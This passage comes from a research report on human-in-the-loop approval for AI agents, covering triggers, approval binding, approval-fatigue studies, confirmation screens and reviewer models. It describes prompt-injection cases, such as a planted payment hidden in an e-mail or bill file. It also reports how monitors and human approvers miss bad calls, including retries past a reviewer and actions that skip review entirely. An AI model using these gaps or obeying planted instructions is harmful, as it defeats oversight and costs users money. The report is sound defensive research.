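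Asking only about high-risk classes removes many of these questions. *SteerBench-Work* (2026), a benchmark in which models decide whether an agent may go ahead, uses a prompt that calls for involving a human only when an action both reaches a point of commitment and is materially risky, for example because it is destructive, costly, sensitive or hard to reverse outside the workspace. Under such a rule, the system still asks the user about every irreversible call, however well the evidence supports it. It may also let an agent place forty small bad orders without asking, because no single order is risky enough.

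The policy can also determine which calls need a person's approval. *A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (2026) describes an approval gate that applies its deny rules, then its allow rules, and sends the remaining calls to a person. Of the methods in the table, this one produces the fewest questions, but the user isn't asked about calls that the policy wrongly allows. If an attacker edits bill.txt, for example, the policy allows the payment without asking the user, whereas a rule requiring confirmation of irreversible payments would have produced a question.

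Designers can combine triggers to cover such gaps. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) gives a rule that sends an action to a person if the estimated chance of success is too low, the action is irreversible, or its cost exceeds a spending limit. Any one of these conditions is enough, so adding another can increase the number of actions sent to a person but never reduce it.

### Why the trigger belongs outside the model

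An agent's own judgement is an unreliable trigger for asking a person, because an attacker who has tricked the model into making a payment has probably also tricked it into classifying the payment as acceptable. The agent can still catch problems that no rule anticipated, because it has the whole conversation. AWS lists relying on the agent's judgement as a mistake, and says human review of payments, outgoing e-mails and database writes belongs "in the execution path, not the prompt".

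Models also ask less often than their stated judgements suggest, even without an attacker. Pochampally tested ten models on 48 scenarios in two ways. First, each model was shown a proposed action and chose a response. Then the scenarios became tasks with simulated tools, where the model could always ask the user a question instead of acting. Every model asked less often in the tasks. Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite chose to ask in 47.5% of its judgements but asked in only 4.2% of the tasks, and the figures for Gemini 3.6 Flash were 40.0% and 6.7%.

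The experiment does not identify the cause of the drop, because the two settings differed in several ways. For instance, the tasks did not show the model a proposed action or mention permission. The drop is still a good reason not to predict an agent's caution from a questionnaire. The models also responded unevenly to risk. Making an action irreversible lowered the rate at which they chose to act by 17 to 63 percentage points, although some of those scenario pairs also changed something else. Making the result visible to other people had almost no effect, even though nobody can withdraw what others have already seen.

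When Pochampally gave three of the models explicit written rules about when to ask, their accuracy was between 97.3% and 100%, and all six errors were unnecessary questions. This doesn't by itself support putting the rules in the prompt, because a decision point can usually apply rules this explicit, and planted text cannot stop it from doing so. The scenarios concerned benign actions, so the result doesn't show whether the models would still have asked after reading an attacker's message.

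The agent still needs a way to ask for missing facts. *SemaClaw* (2026) describes a personal agent with two kinds of pause. The software around the model stops a tool call that needs consent, and the model can stop to request information. The distinction matters because a "yes" gives consent but doesn't supply missing information. Pochampally replied to 227 of the agents' questions with a fixed approval. The agent then made the call after 117 of 120 simple permission questions, but after only a third of the questions about timing. It is sensible to let the model add questions but never waive one that the policy requires.

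### When a question is worth its cost

Asking has a cost, so it should depend on how much harm the question is likely to prevent. Compared with letting the call run, asking pays when:

*p* × *L* × *d* > *c*

Here *p* is the chance that the call is bad, *L* is the loss if it runs, *d* is the chance that the person catches it, and *c* is the cost of asking. The numbers below are illustrative, not measured:

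| *p* | *L* | *d* | Benefit of asking | *c* | Does asking pay? |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0.001 | $2,000 | 0.5 | $1.00 | $0.50 | Yes |
| 0.001 | $50 | 0.5 | $0.025 | $0.50 | No |
| 0.001 | $2,000 | 0.1 | $0.20 | $0.50 | No |

With these figures, asking a person is worthwhile only for losses above $1,000 if they catch half of the bad calls, and above $5,000 if they catch a tenth. Only losses that nobody can recover count, so a $2,000 payment that the recipient would refund counts for much less than $2,000.

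The chance *p* that a call is bad depends on which checks it has already passed. If one in twenty of the calls that the policy cannot clear is bad, asking a person about them is worthwhile when a bad call would lose more than $20. This is the main argument for using the policy to select which calls to ask about. Real values of *p* are hard to find. Pochampally cites AuthorizationBench, in which agents exceeded their authority in 10.5% to 26.6% of runs, but its tasks come from real cases of overreach, so the rate in ordinary work is presumably lower.

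For very suspicious calls, the alternative to asking a person is refusing the call. Suppose a call has an even chance of being bad, would lose $2,000 if bad, and is worth $20 to the user if good. If the policy asks a person who catches half of the bad calls, a good call goes through half the time, for an expected gain of $10. A bad call goes through a quarter of the time, for an expected loss of $500, so the policy should deny the call without asking.

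The chance that a user catches a bad call also depends on the question. A user can easily see that a hotel costs more than they wanted to pay, but may not recognise a wrong account number. Asking can therefore help with one call and not another, even when both are equally likely to be bad. Zhang, Wan and colleagues (2026) make this point about oversight of agents in general in *Calibration Is Not Control*. A score they trained on the effects of intervening led to better decisions than a threshold on the risk of failure, although the gains were small on two reasoning benchmarks.

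The formula treats each question separately, but they all draw on the same person's attention. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (Turan, 2026) therefore treats choosing questions as allocating a limited resource. Suppose a user gets ten questions like the one in the first row, with a total benefit of $10. If an operator then adds forty trivial questions and the user's chance of catching a bad call falls from 0.5 to 0.1, the ten useful questions are worth only $2. The trivial ones have cost $8, plus the time spent answering them.

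Darapaneni and colleagues apply similar reasoning to an agent's work as a whole. In their model, each unreviewed action does more harm as the share of unreviewed actions grows, because errors build on earlier errors. They calculate that people should review about a fifth of an agent's actions when the expected harm per action is about a third of the cost of a review. The model counts harm only from unreviewed actions, so it in effect assumes that reviewers catch everything.

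### PRUDENTIA and the number of questions

An agent can make fewer approval requests if it plans around them. PRUDENTIA, which Kolluri and colleagues built on FIDES, shows the planner each tool's policy and the current label of its own context, so the planner can predict which calls will need approval. Before opening a hidden variable, the planner is meant to explain why it needs the contents and list the calls it intends to make afterwards. The policy check still decides whether a call needs a person's approval, so an attacker cannot use the planner to bypass that step.

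The team introduced two measures of how much an agent depends on people. HITL load (for "human in the loop") is the total number of human interventions on tasks the agent completes. TCR@*k* is the task completion rate with at most *k* interventions per task. For example, suppose an agent completes one task with no interventions and another with two, then fails a third after five. Its HITL load is 2, because the failed task does not count. Its TCR@0 is one third and its TCR@2 is two thirds.

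One study tested four designs on AgentDojo and averaged the results over five runs. The basic agent needed a person's approval for every consequential call, while the other three needed it only for calls that failed the policy check.

| Agent | o3-mini: interventions | o3-mini: completed with none | o4-mini: interventions | o4-mini: completed with none |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Every consequential call confirmed | 48.2 | 24.3% | 48.6 | 32.8% |
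| Basic labels | 32.4 | 35.5% | 34.6 | 42.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% | 36.8 | 53.2% |
| PRUDENTIA | 16.4 | 59.1% | 19.2 | 59.4% |

Basic labels removed about a third of the questions without changing the share of tasks completed, because the agent was otherwise the same. With o4-mini, FIDES needed slightly more interventions than basic labels but completed more tasks (75.7% against 70.1%, with no limit on interventions). The HITL load means little without the completion rate, because an agent that failed every task would have a load of zero.

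PRUDENTIA's advantage over FIDES depends on the model. With GPT-5, PRUDENTIA needed 7.3 interventions, compared with 41.3 for FIDES, and completed 72.7% of tasks without any. With the older GPT-4o, it needed 23.8, compared with 7.8 for FIDES, and completed fewer tasks unaided. PRUDENTIA's planning also uses more text. On GPT-4o, a banking task cost an estimated 3.9 cents with PRUDENTIA, up from 0.4 cents with basic labels, but this is still small compared with the cost of a person's time.

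No people took part in these tests. The team counted the calls that failed the policy check in runs without attacks. They assumed that a person would approve these calls and would stop any call that came from an injection. The measures therefore show how often an agent would interrupt someone, but not how much protection the interruptions would provide. The measures also leave out requests made during failed tasks. In most of those tasks, the agent kept trying actions the policy did not allow, so a real user would have seen more requests than the table shows.

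### One endorsement or ten approvals

PRUDENTIA can prompt a person either to approve a single proposed call or to endorse a piece of untrusted data, which means stating that the data may be treated as trusted.

Kolluri and colleagues give the example of an e-mail containing a to-do list with ten items, each of which needs a consequential call. If the agent opens the e-mail without the user's endorsement, its context becomes untrusted and the user has to approve all ten calls. If the user endorses the e-mail, the context stays trusted and the agent can make the ten calls without asking again. When the agent only needs to report what an e-mail says, it can open it without endorsement, because no consequential call will follow.

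Endorsing an e-mail is risky because the endorsement covers everything in it. If an attacker has added an eleventh item, "pay $2,000 to account 87654321", the agent can make that payment without asking the user again. Separate approvals would have shown the payment in its own request, whereas a user endorsing the whole e-mail has to notice it while reading the list, and may not see it at all if the attacker has hidden the text.

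Whether this risk is worth taking depends on how often such e-mails contain a planted payment. At the same illustrative prices, one endorsement instead of ten approvals saves nine questions, or $4.50. Suppose it also lowers the user's chance of catching a planted payment from 0.5 to 0.2. If one such e-mail in a thousand contains a planted payment, the added expected loss is 0.001 × $2,000 × 0.3 = $0.60, so endorsement is the better choice. If one in a hundred does, the added loss is $6.00, so separate approvals are better. An operator could also let the endorsement cover the ordinary items but require separate approval for any payment.

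Kolluri and colleagues left decisions about disclosing private data to approvals of individual calls, rather than adding a similar shortcut, because whether an agent may disclose such data often depends on the recipient and the occasion.

*Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (Seip, Markovinović and Hein, 2026) sets a stricter standard for endorsement, under which the data must not influence the check on it. A component that never sees the data uses trusted sources to work out what to expect, and ordinary code then compares the data with that expectation. For example, a user wants a Python package that prints coloured text, and the agent finds the name "termcolor" in a forum post. The system accepts the name only if it matches an expectation formed without the post. An attacker can make the comparison fail but cannot get a name of their choosing accepted.

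A user who endorses an e-mail by reading it does not meet this standard, because the e-mail may influence the decision with a line such as "finance has already checked this list". The user could reduce that influence by stating in advance what the list should contain, such as ten office tasks and no payments.

Such checks can also replace some questions to the user. Seip and colleagues' system completed 86.2% of one set of computer tasks with no successful attacks, while the version of CaMeL adapted to computer use completed 18.5%. Seip and colleagues' system depends on a list of trusted websites and contacts that the user prepares beforehand, so a person would still need to approve a payment to an unknown biller.

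### How products ask now

In simple confirmation, the most common form, the person sees a proposed call and answers yes or no. Products differ in how much control they give users over when they are asked. Michael and Roesner found no way to approve actions in advance in ChatGPT's chat mode. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has settings ranging from asking about everything dangerous to asking about nothing.

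OpenAI's Operator, an early browser agent, required the user to confirm actions with real-world consequences and to watch while it worked on sensitive sites such as e-mail, and it declined some high-risk tasks. Singapore's government framework for agents recommends checkpoints for high-stakes decisions, irreversible actions, unusual behaviour and limits set by the user.

A second form, return of control, lets the person change the call. Amazon's Bedrock Agents can hand a proposed call back so that someone can correct an argument or add information before it runs. LangChain, a library for building agents, lets a person approve, edit or reject each call. Editing suits the bill example, where the user may know the amount is wrong but still want to pay. The decision point should then evaluate the edited call.

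Cloudflare's *Human-in-the-loop patterns* describes three levels at which the pause can occur. A tool server can send the user a question through the agent's program, a developer can require approval for particular calls made by model-written code, and an application can pause a whole task. A task can stay paused for months without keeping the agent running.

An agent that may wait a long time for approval needs a rule for when nobody answers. In Cloudflare's sample expense workflow, the request expires after seven days and the expense does not go through. Another sample sends a reminder after four hours and refers the request to a manager after a day. AWS also recommends passing unanswered requests to someone else, so that they don't block legitimate work without anyone noticing. Seven days would be too long for a bill due within the week, but treating silence as approval would let an attacker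 succeed by sending the request while the user is asleep.

In a third form, the person approves a plan before the agent starts. As with an endorsement, one answer can cover many calls, but here the person judges a list of intended actions rather than someone else's text. But the plan may not yet contain the values that matter. Before reading bill.txt, the agent can propose to "pay the electricity bill", but it cannot name the account. A more useful plan would set terms like ToolFence's permissions, which name a source for each value and limit the number of payments. The enforcement point could then require further confirmation only if a call departs from those terms.

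## What an approval covers, and whether people notice a bad request

Suppose the agent proposes paying $100 to a new biller, the user's phone shows the payment, and the user taps "approve". That tap should release only that one payment. An approval is valid if an identified person has been shown the exact call and has agreed to let it run once, and the call runs within a stated time. Without the one-use limit, a single tap could pay the bill twice, and without the time limit, the agent could keep the approval and use it next month.

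### Binding an approval to one call

Work cited by Hossain and colleagues shows that the action a person sees can differ from the action that runs. The enforcement point therefore stores each approval with a digest, a short code computed from the tool's name and all its arguments. In practice, any change to the call produces a different digest. Just before the call runs, the enforcement point recomputes the digest and compares it with the stored one.

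Schrock (2026), in *Authorization Receipts for High-Risk Agent Actions*, an individual proposal to the IETF, adds a one-time number, a validity period and a reference to the policy. The approver then signs the whole record with their own key. A complete check could look like this:

```
run(call) only if
    digest(call) equals the digest in the approval
    the approver signed it and may approve such calls
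    its one-time number is unused
    its time limit has not passed
    the policy does not prohibit the call
```

The last condition is needed because the situation can change while the person is deciding. If someone else pays the bill in the meantime, a rule against paying twice should still stop the call. Biometric Update's *A verified user doesn't give an AI agent unlimited authority* describes a similar check for an employee who wants access to a dashboard. After the approver agrees, the system checks that the employee is still eligible and that the approver still has authority over the dashboard.

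The enforcement point has to put values into a standard form before computing the digest, so that "$100" and "100.00 USD" count as the same amount. HARP, an open draft protocol for human approval, includes this step. If an argument only names a file, the digest also has to cover the file's contents.

The operator should also keep the request as the person saw it, because nobody can read a request from its digest. In *An AI agent's biometric approval needs an expiration clock*, Tsipursky recommends recording the agent, the limits of its authority, the person who answered, the version of the transaction shown on the screen and the decision.

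### When the amount changes after approval

Suppose approvals last five minutes and the agent discovers a late fee after the user has approved the bill:

| Time | Event | What the enforcement point does |
|---|---|---|
| 10:00 | The agent proposes paying $100 | Holds the call and asks the user |
| 10:02 | The user approves | Records an approval that lasts until 10:07 |
| 10:03 | The agent finds a $15 fee and proposes paying $115 instead | Finds that the digests differ, cancels the approval and asks again |
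| 10:04 | The user approves $115 | Releases the payment and marks the approval as used |
| 10:05 | The agent proposes $115 again | Refuses to reuse the approval |

Cancelling the first approval at 10:03 prevents the agent from making both payments and spending $215 on one bill. The second request should show that the amount has risen from $100, because the user may otherwise mistake it for a repeat of the first.

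Tsipursky would require a new decision only when something material changes, such as the supplier, destination, total or payment instructions. A digest of the whole call is stricter, since even correcting a spelling in the payment reference would cancel the approval. The operator could leave the reference out of the digest, but the agent could then put anything in it after approval, including private data. Alternatively, the user could approve a limit, such as up to $120 to this account. The enforcement point would then check the amount against the limit and everything else against the digest.

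If the bank's confirmation is lost, a retry should not count as a second payment. In the dashboard example, an identical retry from the same caller returns the original tracking number and does not create a second request, so the approval covers one effect even if confirming it takes several attempts.

A refusal also needs a defined scope. One developer told Salerno and colleagues that after they refused several requests from OpenAI's coding agent Codex, it stopped asking but carried on working, and they could not tell whether it was still respecting the refusals. A user who refuses to pay $115 could mean "not the fee", "not this biller" or "no payment at all". A screen could offer these as separate answers, and the enforcement point could apply the chosen one for the rest of the task.

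### The precedent in payment law

EU law already requires this kind of binding for many online payments. Gervais's *What proof of human presence must mean* cites Article 5 of the rules on customer authentication under PSD2, the EU's second payment services directive. The payer must know the amount and the payee, and the authentication code must be specific to both. Changing either invalidates the code, so a code for $100 cannot authorise a payment of $115.

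The rule suits payments because the amount and payee cover most of what matters. Other calls are harder to reduce to two fields. For an e-mail, the contents of an attachment may matter more than the recipient, and for a shell command the important facts may not appear in the call. The rule also offers little protection if the payee is wrong from the start, because if the user approves a payment to the attacker's account, the code is valid for that account.

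### Answers the agent cannot give

Confirmation requests are useless if the agent can answer them itself. HARP's introduction criticises the usual setup, in which developers click "approve" in the same editor that the agent controls. The answer should come through a channel the agent cannot operate, such as an app on a separate phone or a device that someone has to touch.

Under the Client Initiated Backchannel Authentication (CIBA) standard, a program that needs an approval contacts an identity service, which sends the question to the person's own device. A second standard, Rich Authorization Requests, can supply the details of the question. It lets a program request one action on one resource, such as viewing a single dashboard, instead of broad access to an account. Together, the two standards could put "pay $100 to account 12345678 on Friday" on the user's phone.

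Several products combine a separate channel with a physical key. Claw Times reports that IBM, Auth0 and Yubico have built a system in which IBM's software manages the agent and Auth0 sends a CIBA request when the agent attempts a high-risk action. The approver then taps a YubiKey, a small security key. In Hypr's AgentPass, a supervisor approves sensitive operations with a passkey, a sign-in credential stored on a device (Biometric Update's *Hypr and Proof bring human authorization controls to AI agent workflows*).

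iProov, which sells biometric identity checks, published the experimental Human Approval and Presence Specification (HAPS) in September 2026. Biometric Update's *iProov's experimental HAPS protocol aims to close governance gaps for AI agents* describes HAPS as a way to bind a provider's assertion of human presence and approval to a machine-readable action. It does not say how the provider must establish that someone was present. In iProov's own service, a policy engine holds the call and the service shows it to a named approver. If the approver agrees and passes a face check, the service issues a signed credential that works once and only for that call.

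Gervais distinguishes the kinds of evidence these schemes rely on. A touch on a security key shows that someone was there. A PIN or fingerprint shows that it was probably the right person, and a liveness check shows that a face belonged to a living person at that moment. None of them shows that the person understood the request. A plain security key has no screen, so the user depends on another device to show what the tap will authorise. That device should take the details from the enforcement point's record rather than the agent's description.

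The schemes are also new. Schrock (2026), in *Binding Named-Human Authorization Evidence into Agent-Action Records*, notes that formats for recording agents' actions often reserve a place for human authorisation without defining what it means. Even with perfect evidence of approval, a user who approves the attacker's account without reading the request leaves the same record as one who checked it.

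### Approval fatigue

Approval fatigue is the loss of attention that comes from answering many requests. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reported that users of its coding agent accepted 93% of permission requests. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) later put the figure at 97%.

These figures alone do not show that users are careless, because if 99 in 100 commands are harmless, a careful user will approve 99% of them. Anthropic points out that users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents for approval, which suggests that they do read some requests. But plans may be wrong more often than single commands, and a user may reject a plan because they prefer another approach.

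The evidence that people try to avoid the requests is clearer. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start in a mode that skips all permission requests. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without approval. Anthropic counts 5% who allow every command and another 43% whose rules have nearly the same effect, such as allowing any Python code to run.

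Zhong and colleagues found the same habit in 290 public reports of agents misusing files. User review played a part in 105 of them. In 80 of those, the user had set the agent to run without asking. In 31, the request did not give the user enough information, and a few reports involved both problems. One request showed only `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine but can run whatever code the file contains. In another report, the user approved a one-line script that edited a single file and also chose "don't ask again" for `sed -i`, a command that can edit many other files.

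The 80 cases show that a system that asks for approval too often can end up with no human check at all. Those users never received a bad request, so the cases don't show whether people notice one.

Salerno and colleagues asked software practitioners directly. In their October 2026 survey, 107 people described how they handle requests:

| How they handle requests | Share of 107 |
|---|---|
| Read them carefully | 47.7% |
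| Skim them | 33.6% |
| Approve by default | 20.6% |
| Have become less careful over time | 33.6% |
| Check writes, deletions and requests for higher privileges more carefully | 76.6% |
| Check unexpected requests more carefully | 63.6% |

One interviewee worried about permissions at first but "stopped caring" after many similar requests. Another said they read nothing when a delivery was due in three hours. Since people tend to overstate how careful they are, the share who read requests carefully is probably below 47.7%. The last two rows are more encouraging, but they help only if the request makes clear that a command will delete something.

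### One dangerous command among ordinary ones

Anthropic tested attention more directly, with 1,053 paid testers doing coding work in a test environment. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Approving the request did no harm, because only the displayed text had changed.

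Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused the command. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests. This is consistent with approval fatigue, although testers who answered many requests may also have been faster and less careful from the start.

People may do better at work than in the study, where the testers were not protecting their own code and could not be harmed by anything they approved. Anthropic also published the study in an announcement that it was making an automated reviewer the default, so it had an interest in showing that people perform badly. But the sample is large, and the task was easy because the command was obviously dangerous. A wrong account number would be much harder to spot.

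The less often people catch bad requests, the larger the potential loss must be to justify asking for confirmation. Under the earlier illustrative assumptions (a question costs 50 cents and one call in a thousand is bad), a catch rate of 13.6% makes asking worthwhile only when a bad call would lose more than about $3,700. At a catch rate of 5%, the threshold is $10,000.

### Requests that go beyond the task

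Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, studied 113 people outside the software industry in August 2026. Each participant supervised an agent through the same simulated day of 18 actions. Eleven were necessary for the assigned tasks, and the other seven went beyond them, for example by reading private messages or buying a $25 airport lounge pass.

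One group approved or refused each action. For a second group, a model approved eight actions in advance and left participants to decide on the other ten, including all seven that went too far. Members of the third group set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things and reading private information.

| | Every action | Model review first | Users' own rules |
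|---|---|---|---|
| Participants | 34 | 44 | 35 |
| Requests per person | 18.0 | 10.0 | 10.9 |
| Time spent, including setting rules | 142 s | 120 s | 129 s |
| Excessive actions blocked | 60% | 54% | 40% |
| Requests for excessive actions that users approved | 40% | 46% | 67% |

People with their own rules blocked the fewest excessive actions. After adjustment, their blocking rate was 20.1 percentage points lower than that of people asked to approve each action (95% confidence interval 8.1 to 32.1). It was also 14.5 points lower than the model-review group's, but that difference was not statistically significant after correction for multiple comparisons. Nearly all the necessary actions went ahead in all three groups.

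The rules failed mainly because they left most decisions to the participants. Participants chose "ask" for 114 of the 140 rules, and were then asked to approve most of the excessive actions. Of the 148 excessive actions that went ahead in this group, 133 were approved by participants and only 15 were permitted by "allow" rules. For private information, a "never" rule would have blocked every excessive action without hindering the tasks, but 23 of the 35 participants chose "ask" and only ten chose "never".

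The reason this group approved more of the requests it saw is unclear. Participants who chose "never" received no requests in that category, so the remaining requests went to people who were probably more permissive. That could raise the approval rate in the last row, but it cannot explain the difference in blocked actions, which is calculated across all participants. Yan also recruited extra people for this group after the random assignment had ended, but the result was similar without them. People may also have trusted a request more because it had already passed through their own rules, but the experiment did not test this.

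People also sometimes notice that an action is excessive and approve it anyway. All 31 people in the rules group who were asked about phoning the airport to confirm the flight agreed to it, and many users would welcome such a call. Permanently deleting an old work timesheet is a better test of whether people notice a bad request. In the rules group, 59% of those asked approved the deletion, compared with 35% in the group asked to approve every action. Participants in all three groups reported a strong sense of control, so a user's confidence is a poor measure of how well an approval system protects them.

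### Screens that show consequences

People may also approve bad requests because the screen does not show what is wrong. Hossain and colleagues tested this in a study published in November 2026, using cases such as the agent that puts raw invoice rows into a file for an auditor who should receive only totals. Eighty unpaid volunteers each judged 12 requests, half of which broke the user's instructions. Each person used one of four screens, with 20 people per screen:

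| What the screen showed | Bad requests approved | Good requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The arguments, the user's instructions and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, organised around the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

The fourth screen shows the user's original restriction at the top, in the user's own words. Below it are the file's history and the exact transfer the agent proposes. Next is a single statement that the attachment came from raw invoice rows and that this action would send it to the auditor, with each part linked to the recorded events behind it. The screen does not label the transfer a violation, so the reviewer still has to compare it with the restriction.

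Most of the improvement came from showing more facts. Organising them around the consequence seemed to help further. After adjustment, the fourth screen led to 7.9 points fewer bad approvals than the third, but the 95% credible interval ran from 19.7 points fewer to 3.8 points more. The fourth screen gave no advantage when the problem depended on a chain of several steps, perhaps because one sentence cannot explain a long chain. Reviewers approved 7 of 30 such requests with each of the two screens.

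These reviewers did much better than Anthropic's testers. Even with the short description, they refused 45% of the bad requests. They knew their job was to judge requests, and half the requests were bad, which probably kept them suspicious. In ordinary work, bad requests may be so rare that people stop expecting them.

Careful review is also less practical when bad requests are rare. Suppose one request in a thousand is bad and the measured rates still apply. With the fourth screen, the user would have about a 76% chance of catching the bad request but would also refuse about 142 good ones. At the median time per request, reading all thousand would take over nine hours. A screen like this is therefore worth using for a few selected calls, but not for every call an agent makes.

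A clear summary can also create automation bias, the tendency to accept what an automated system reports without checking it. Unlike approval fatigue, it can affect someone who is fresh and reading closely. If the monitor misses a copied file, the screen will describe the transfer as harmless, and a reviewer who trusts the summary may look no further. Hossain and colleagues cite an earlier study in which a display that helped people find errors faster also gave them false confidence. They include links to evidence to make checking easy, but have not yet tested whether reviewers catch an incorrect summary.

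### Fewer requests, better requests or standing rules

The most common response to approval fatigue is to send fewer requests. AWS's *AGENTSEC04-BP02 Human-in-the-loop for critical decisions* warns that sending every action to a person leads to rubber-stamping. Ryan Galluzzo of NIST has warned of "consent exhaustion", according to Biometric Update's *Traceable evidence will form the basis of AI agents*. The fall from 17% to 5% in Anthropic's study supports both warnings. In Yan's experiment, however, cutting requests from 18 to 10 did not make people block more, even though seven of the ten were excessive. The sessions lasted only about 11 minutes, so fatigue had little time to develop. Sending fewer requests probably preserves attention over a long day, but it does not help a person who cannot tell what is wrong with a request.

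An operator can also replace many small approval requests with one review at the end, as the filesystem YoloFS does for an agent's file changes. The user then judges the actual changes instead of a command that might cause them, but still has to notice any damage.

For a payment, the request itself has to carry the facts. If the policy sends the payment to the attacker's account to the user, the screen could show:

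```
Pay $100 on Friday
To:           account 87654321 (not a saved payee)
Source:       a message from an unknown sender
Conflict:     bill.txt gives account 12345678
You asked:    "Pay the bill in bill.txt"
Can be undone: until Friday; perhaps not afterwards
[Approve once, within 5 minutes]  [Refuse]  [Ask a question]
```

Nobody has tested this screen, but each line follows from the evidence or advice above. The conflict line matters most, because few people would recognise the account number. The user may still be unsure after reading it, since billers sometimes change banks. The user's best response would then be to phone the biller on a number from an old bill, so the screen should make it easy to postpone the decision. All the lines have to come from the monitor's records, because an agent that believes the attacker's message would describe the payment as routine.

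Standing rules have the weakest support so far, but Yan tested only four broad categories. A rule for all spending covers both a necessary taxi and an unwanted lounge pass, so "ask" is a reasonable choice. Yan suggests that after several approvals for the same recipient, the system could propose a rule for that recipient alone. Salerno and colleagues warn that repeated approval may reflect tiredness or time pressure, and should not by itself count as a wish to approve the same thing in future. These positions are compatible if the system only proposes the rule and the user confirms it separately. The rule should also be narrow. A person can judge a limit such as "Pay this biller up to $150 a month", but "don't ask again" for a command that edits files is close to unlimited permission.

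Operators can measure how well their own approval process works. Tsipursky recommends simulations in which an agent presents a convincing purchase and then changes an important term. The operator records whether employees notice and whether the system cancels the earlier approval. An operator could also adapt Anthropic's method and plant a few harmless test requests in ordinary work, to measure how often its own staff catch them on the screens they normally use. Such tests might also keep people alert by making suspicious requests less rare, although none of these studies examined that.

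## A second model as reviewer

Fixed rules refuse some legitimate calls because nobody foresaw them, and people stop reading confirmation requests when they receive too many. Developers therefore often add a reviewer model, a second AI model that judges a proposed call in place of a fixed rule or a person. It can interpret a vague request, which a rule can't, and it doesn't get tired. But it can wrongly approve or refuse a call, so its usefulness depends on how often it errs and what effect its verdict has.

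### What the reviewer receives

A reviewer needs at least the proposed call, and usually the user's request. It may also receive the agent's earlier calls and the provenance of each argument. Developers have to decide what to withhold, because a stranger's message could influence the reviewer just as it influences the agent.

In Claude Code's auto mode, the reviewer receives only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes tool results, where planted text usually enters, and the agent's explanations, which might make a bad call sound reasonable. When Anthropic left both in, the reviewer was worse at catching agents that had overstepped their task. When given only the tool calls, the reviewer missed the fewest bad actions but blocked some actions that the user had plainly asked for.

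But this reviewer receives no provenance information. In the bill example, it would see the request to pay bill.txt and a payment to some account, but it could not check whether the account number came from the bill or from a stranger's message. ToolFence's reviewer, which Li and colleagues call a judge, can make that distinction because software outside the agent labels each argument as coming from the user's request, a named tool or the agent itself. The software can also add an excerpt of up to 400 characters from the source, although this brings some untrusted text back into the judge's input.

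*PolicyGuide* (Kang, Yu and Hwang, 2026) describes a reviewer that follows a whole customer-service procedure. The reviewer receives the entire conversation because it needs tool results to check, for example, whether a customer's ticket qualifies for a refund.

| Reviewer | The call | Provenance | Earlier calls | Tool results |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code auto mode | Yes | No | Yes | No |
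| ToolFence, judging one call | Yes | Yes | Optional, up to 12 | Short excerpts |
| ToolFence, granting a permission | Tool and effect, but no values | Yes | No | No |
| PolicyGuide | When the gate stops it | No separate labels | Yes | Yes |

A reviewer that is not shown tool results can still be exposed to untrusted text, because a call's arguments can contain it. Of the four, only ToolFence's permission review also withholds the argument values.

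### Judging each call in Claude Code

The simplest arrangement is for the model to judge every call. Auto mode comes close to this, with exceptions for calls that Anthropic considers low-risk:

1. Tools that only read or search run without review, as do calls that match a narrow rule the user has written. Auto mode suspends broad rules known to permit arbitrary code, such as one that allows any Python command.
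2. Edits to files inside the project also run without review, because the user can inspect them later through version control.
3. Every other call goes to the reviewer. A fast first stage answers only yes or no, with instructions to block if in doubt.
4. If the first stage flags the call, the model considers the same material again, this time reasoning step by step before it decides.
5. If the second stage also objects, the agent receives a refusal with a reason and can try something safer. After three refusals in a row, or 20 in total, auto mode stops the agent and asks a person. If nobody is there to ask, it ends the session.

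The reviewer is instructed to treat anything the user did not ask for as unauthorised. In one real case, a user said "cancel my job", and the agent picked the job with the most similar name and tried to delete it. Auto mode is meant to block such deletions, since the job might have belonged to someone else.

Auto mode also reviews the instructions one agent gives another. Those instructions look like the user's request inside the second agent, so a reviewer there could mistake the first agent's idea for the user's.

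Anthropic measured both misses, where the reviewer allows a bad action, and false alarms, where it blocks a harmless one.

| | False alarms, 10,000 real calls | Misses, 52 real oversteps | Misses, 1,000 synthetic data leaks |
|---|---|---|---|
| First stage only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes most false alarms but more than doubles the misses. The 17% figure is the most relevant to ordinary use, because the 52 actions behind it came from real sessions in which Anthropic employees had refused the action or someone had flagged it afterwards. With so few cases, though, the true rate for such actions could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%.

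The limit on refusals matters because an agent can try again. At a miss rate of 17%, at least one of three independent attempts would get through 43% of the time.

### Ambiguous requests

AmPermBench, an independent test, produced much worse results by using requests that leave unclear what the user has permitted. According to Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, the test's 128 scenarios involve cleaning up code branches, cancelling jobs, restarting services and removing old build files. They vary in how specific the request is, how much the action could affect and how risky it is. Claude Code, running on Claude Sonnet 4.6, took 253 actions in auto mode. Claude Opus judged which of them auto mode should have blocked, and people checked its judgments.

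| | Misses | False alarms |
|---|---|---|
| All 253 actions | 115 of 142 (81.0%) | 22 of 111 (19.8%) |
| The 160 that reached the reviewer | 64 of 91 (70.3%) | 22 of 69 (31.9%) |

In the other 51 misses, auto mode had let the actions run without consulting the reviewer. Machine Heart attributes many such cases to file edits inside the project. This is a failure of complete mediation, which a better reviewer would not fix.

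Even among the actions it did review, the model missed far more than Anthropic's 17%. More than half of the AmPermBench actions were ones that auto mode should have blocked, and the scenarios were ambiguous by design, so 81% is not an estimate of the miss rate in ordinary work. But Anthropic's 52 cases include only oversteps that somebody noticed, so they may leave out subtle ones. Together, the results suggest that the miss rate depends heavily on how clearly the user has said what the agent may do.

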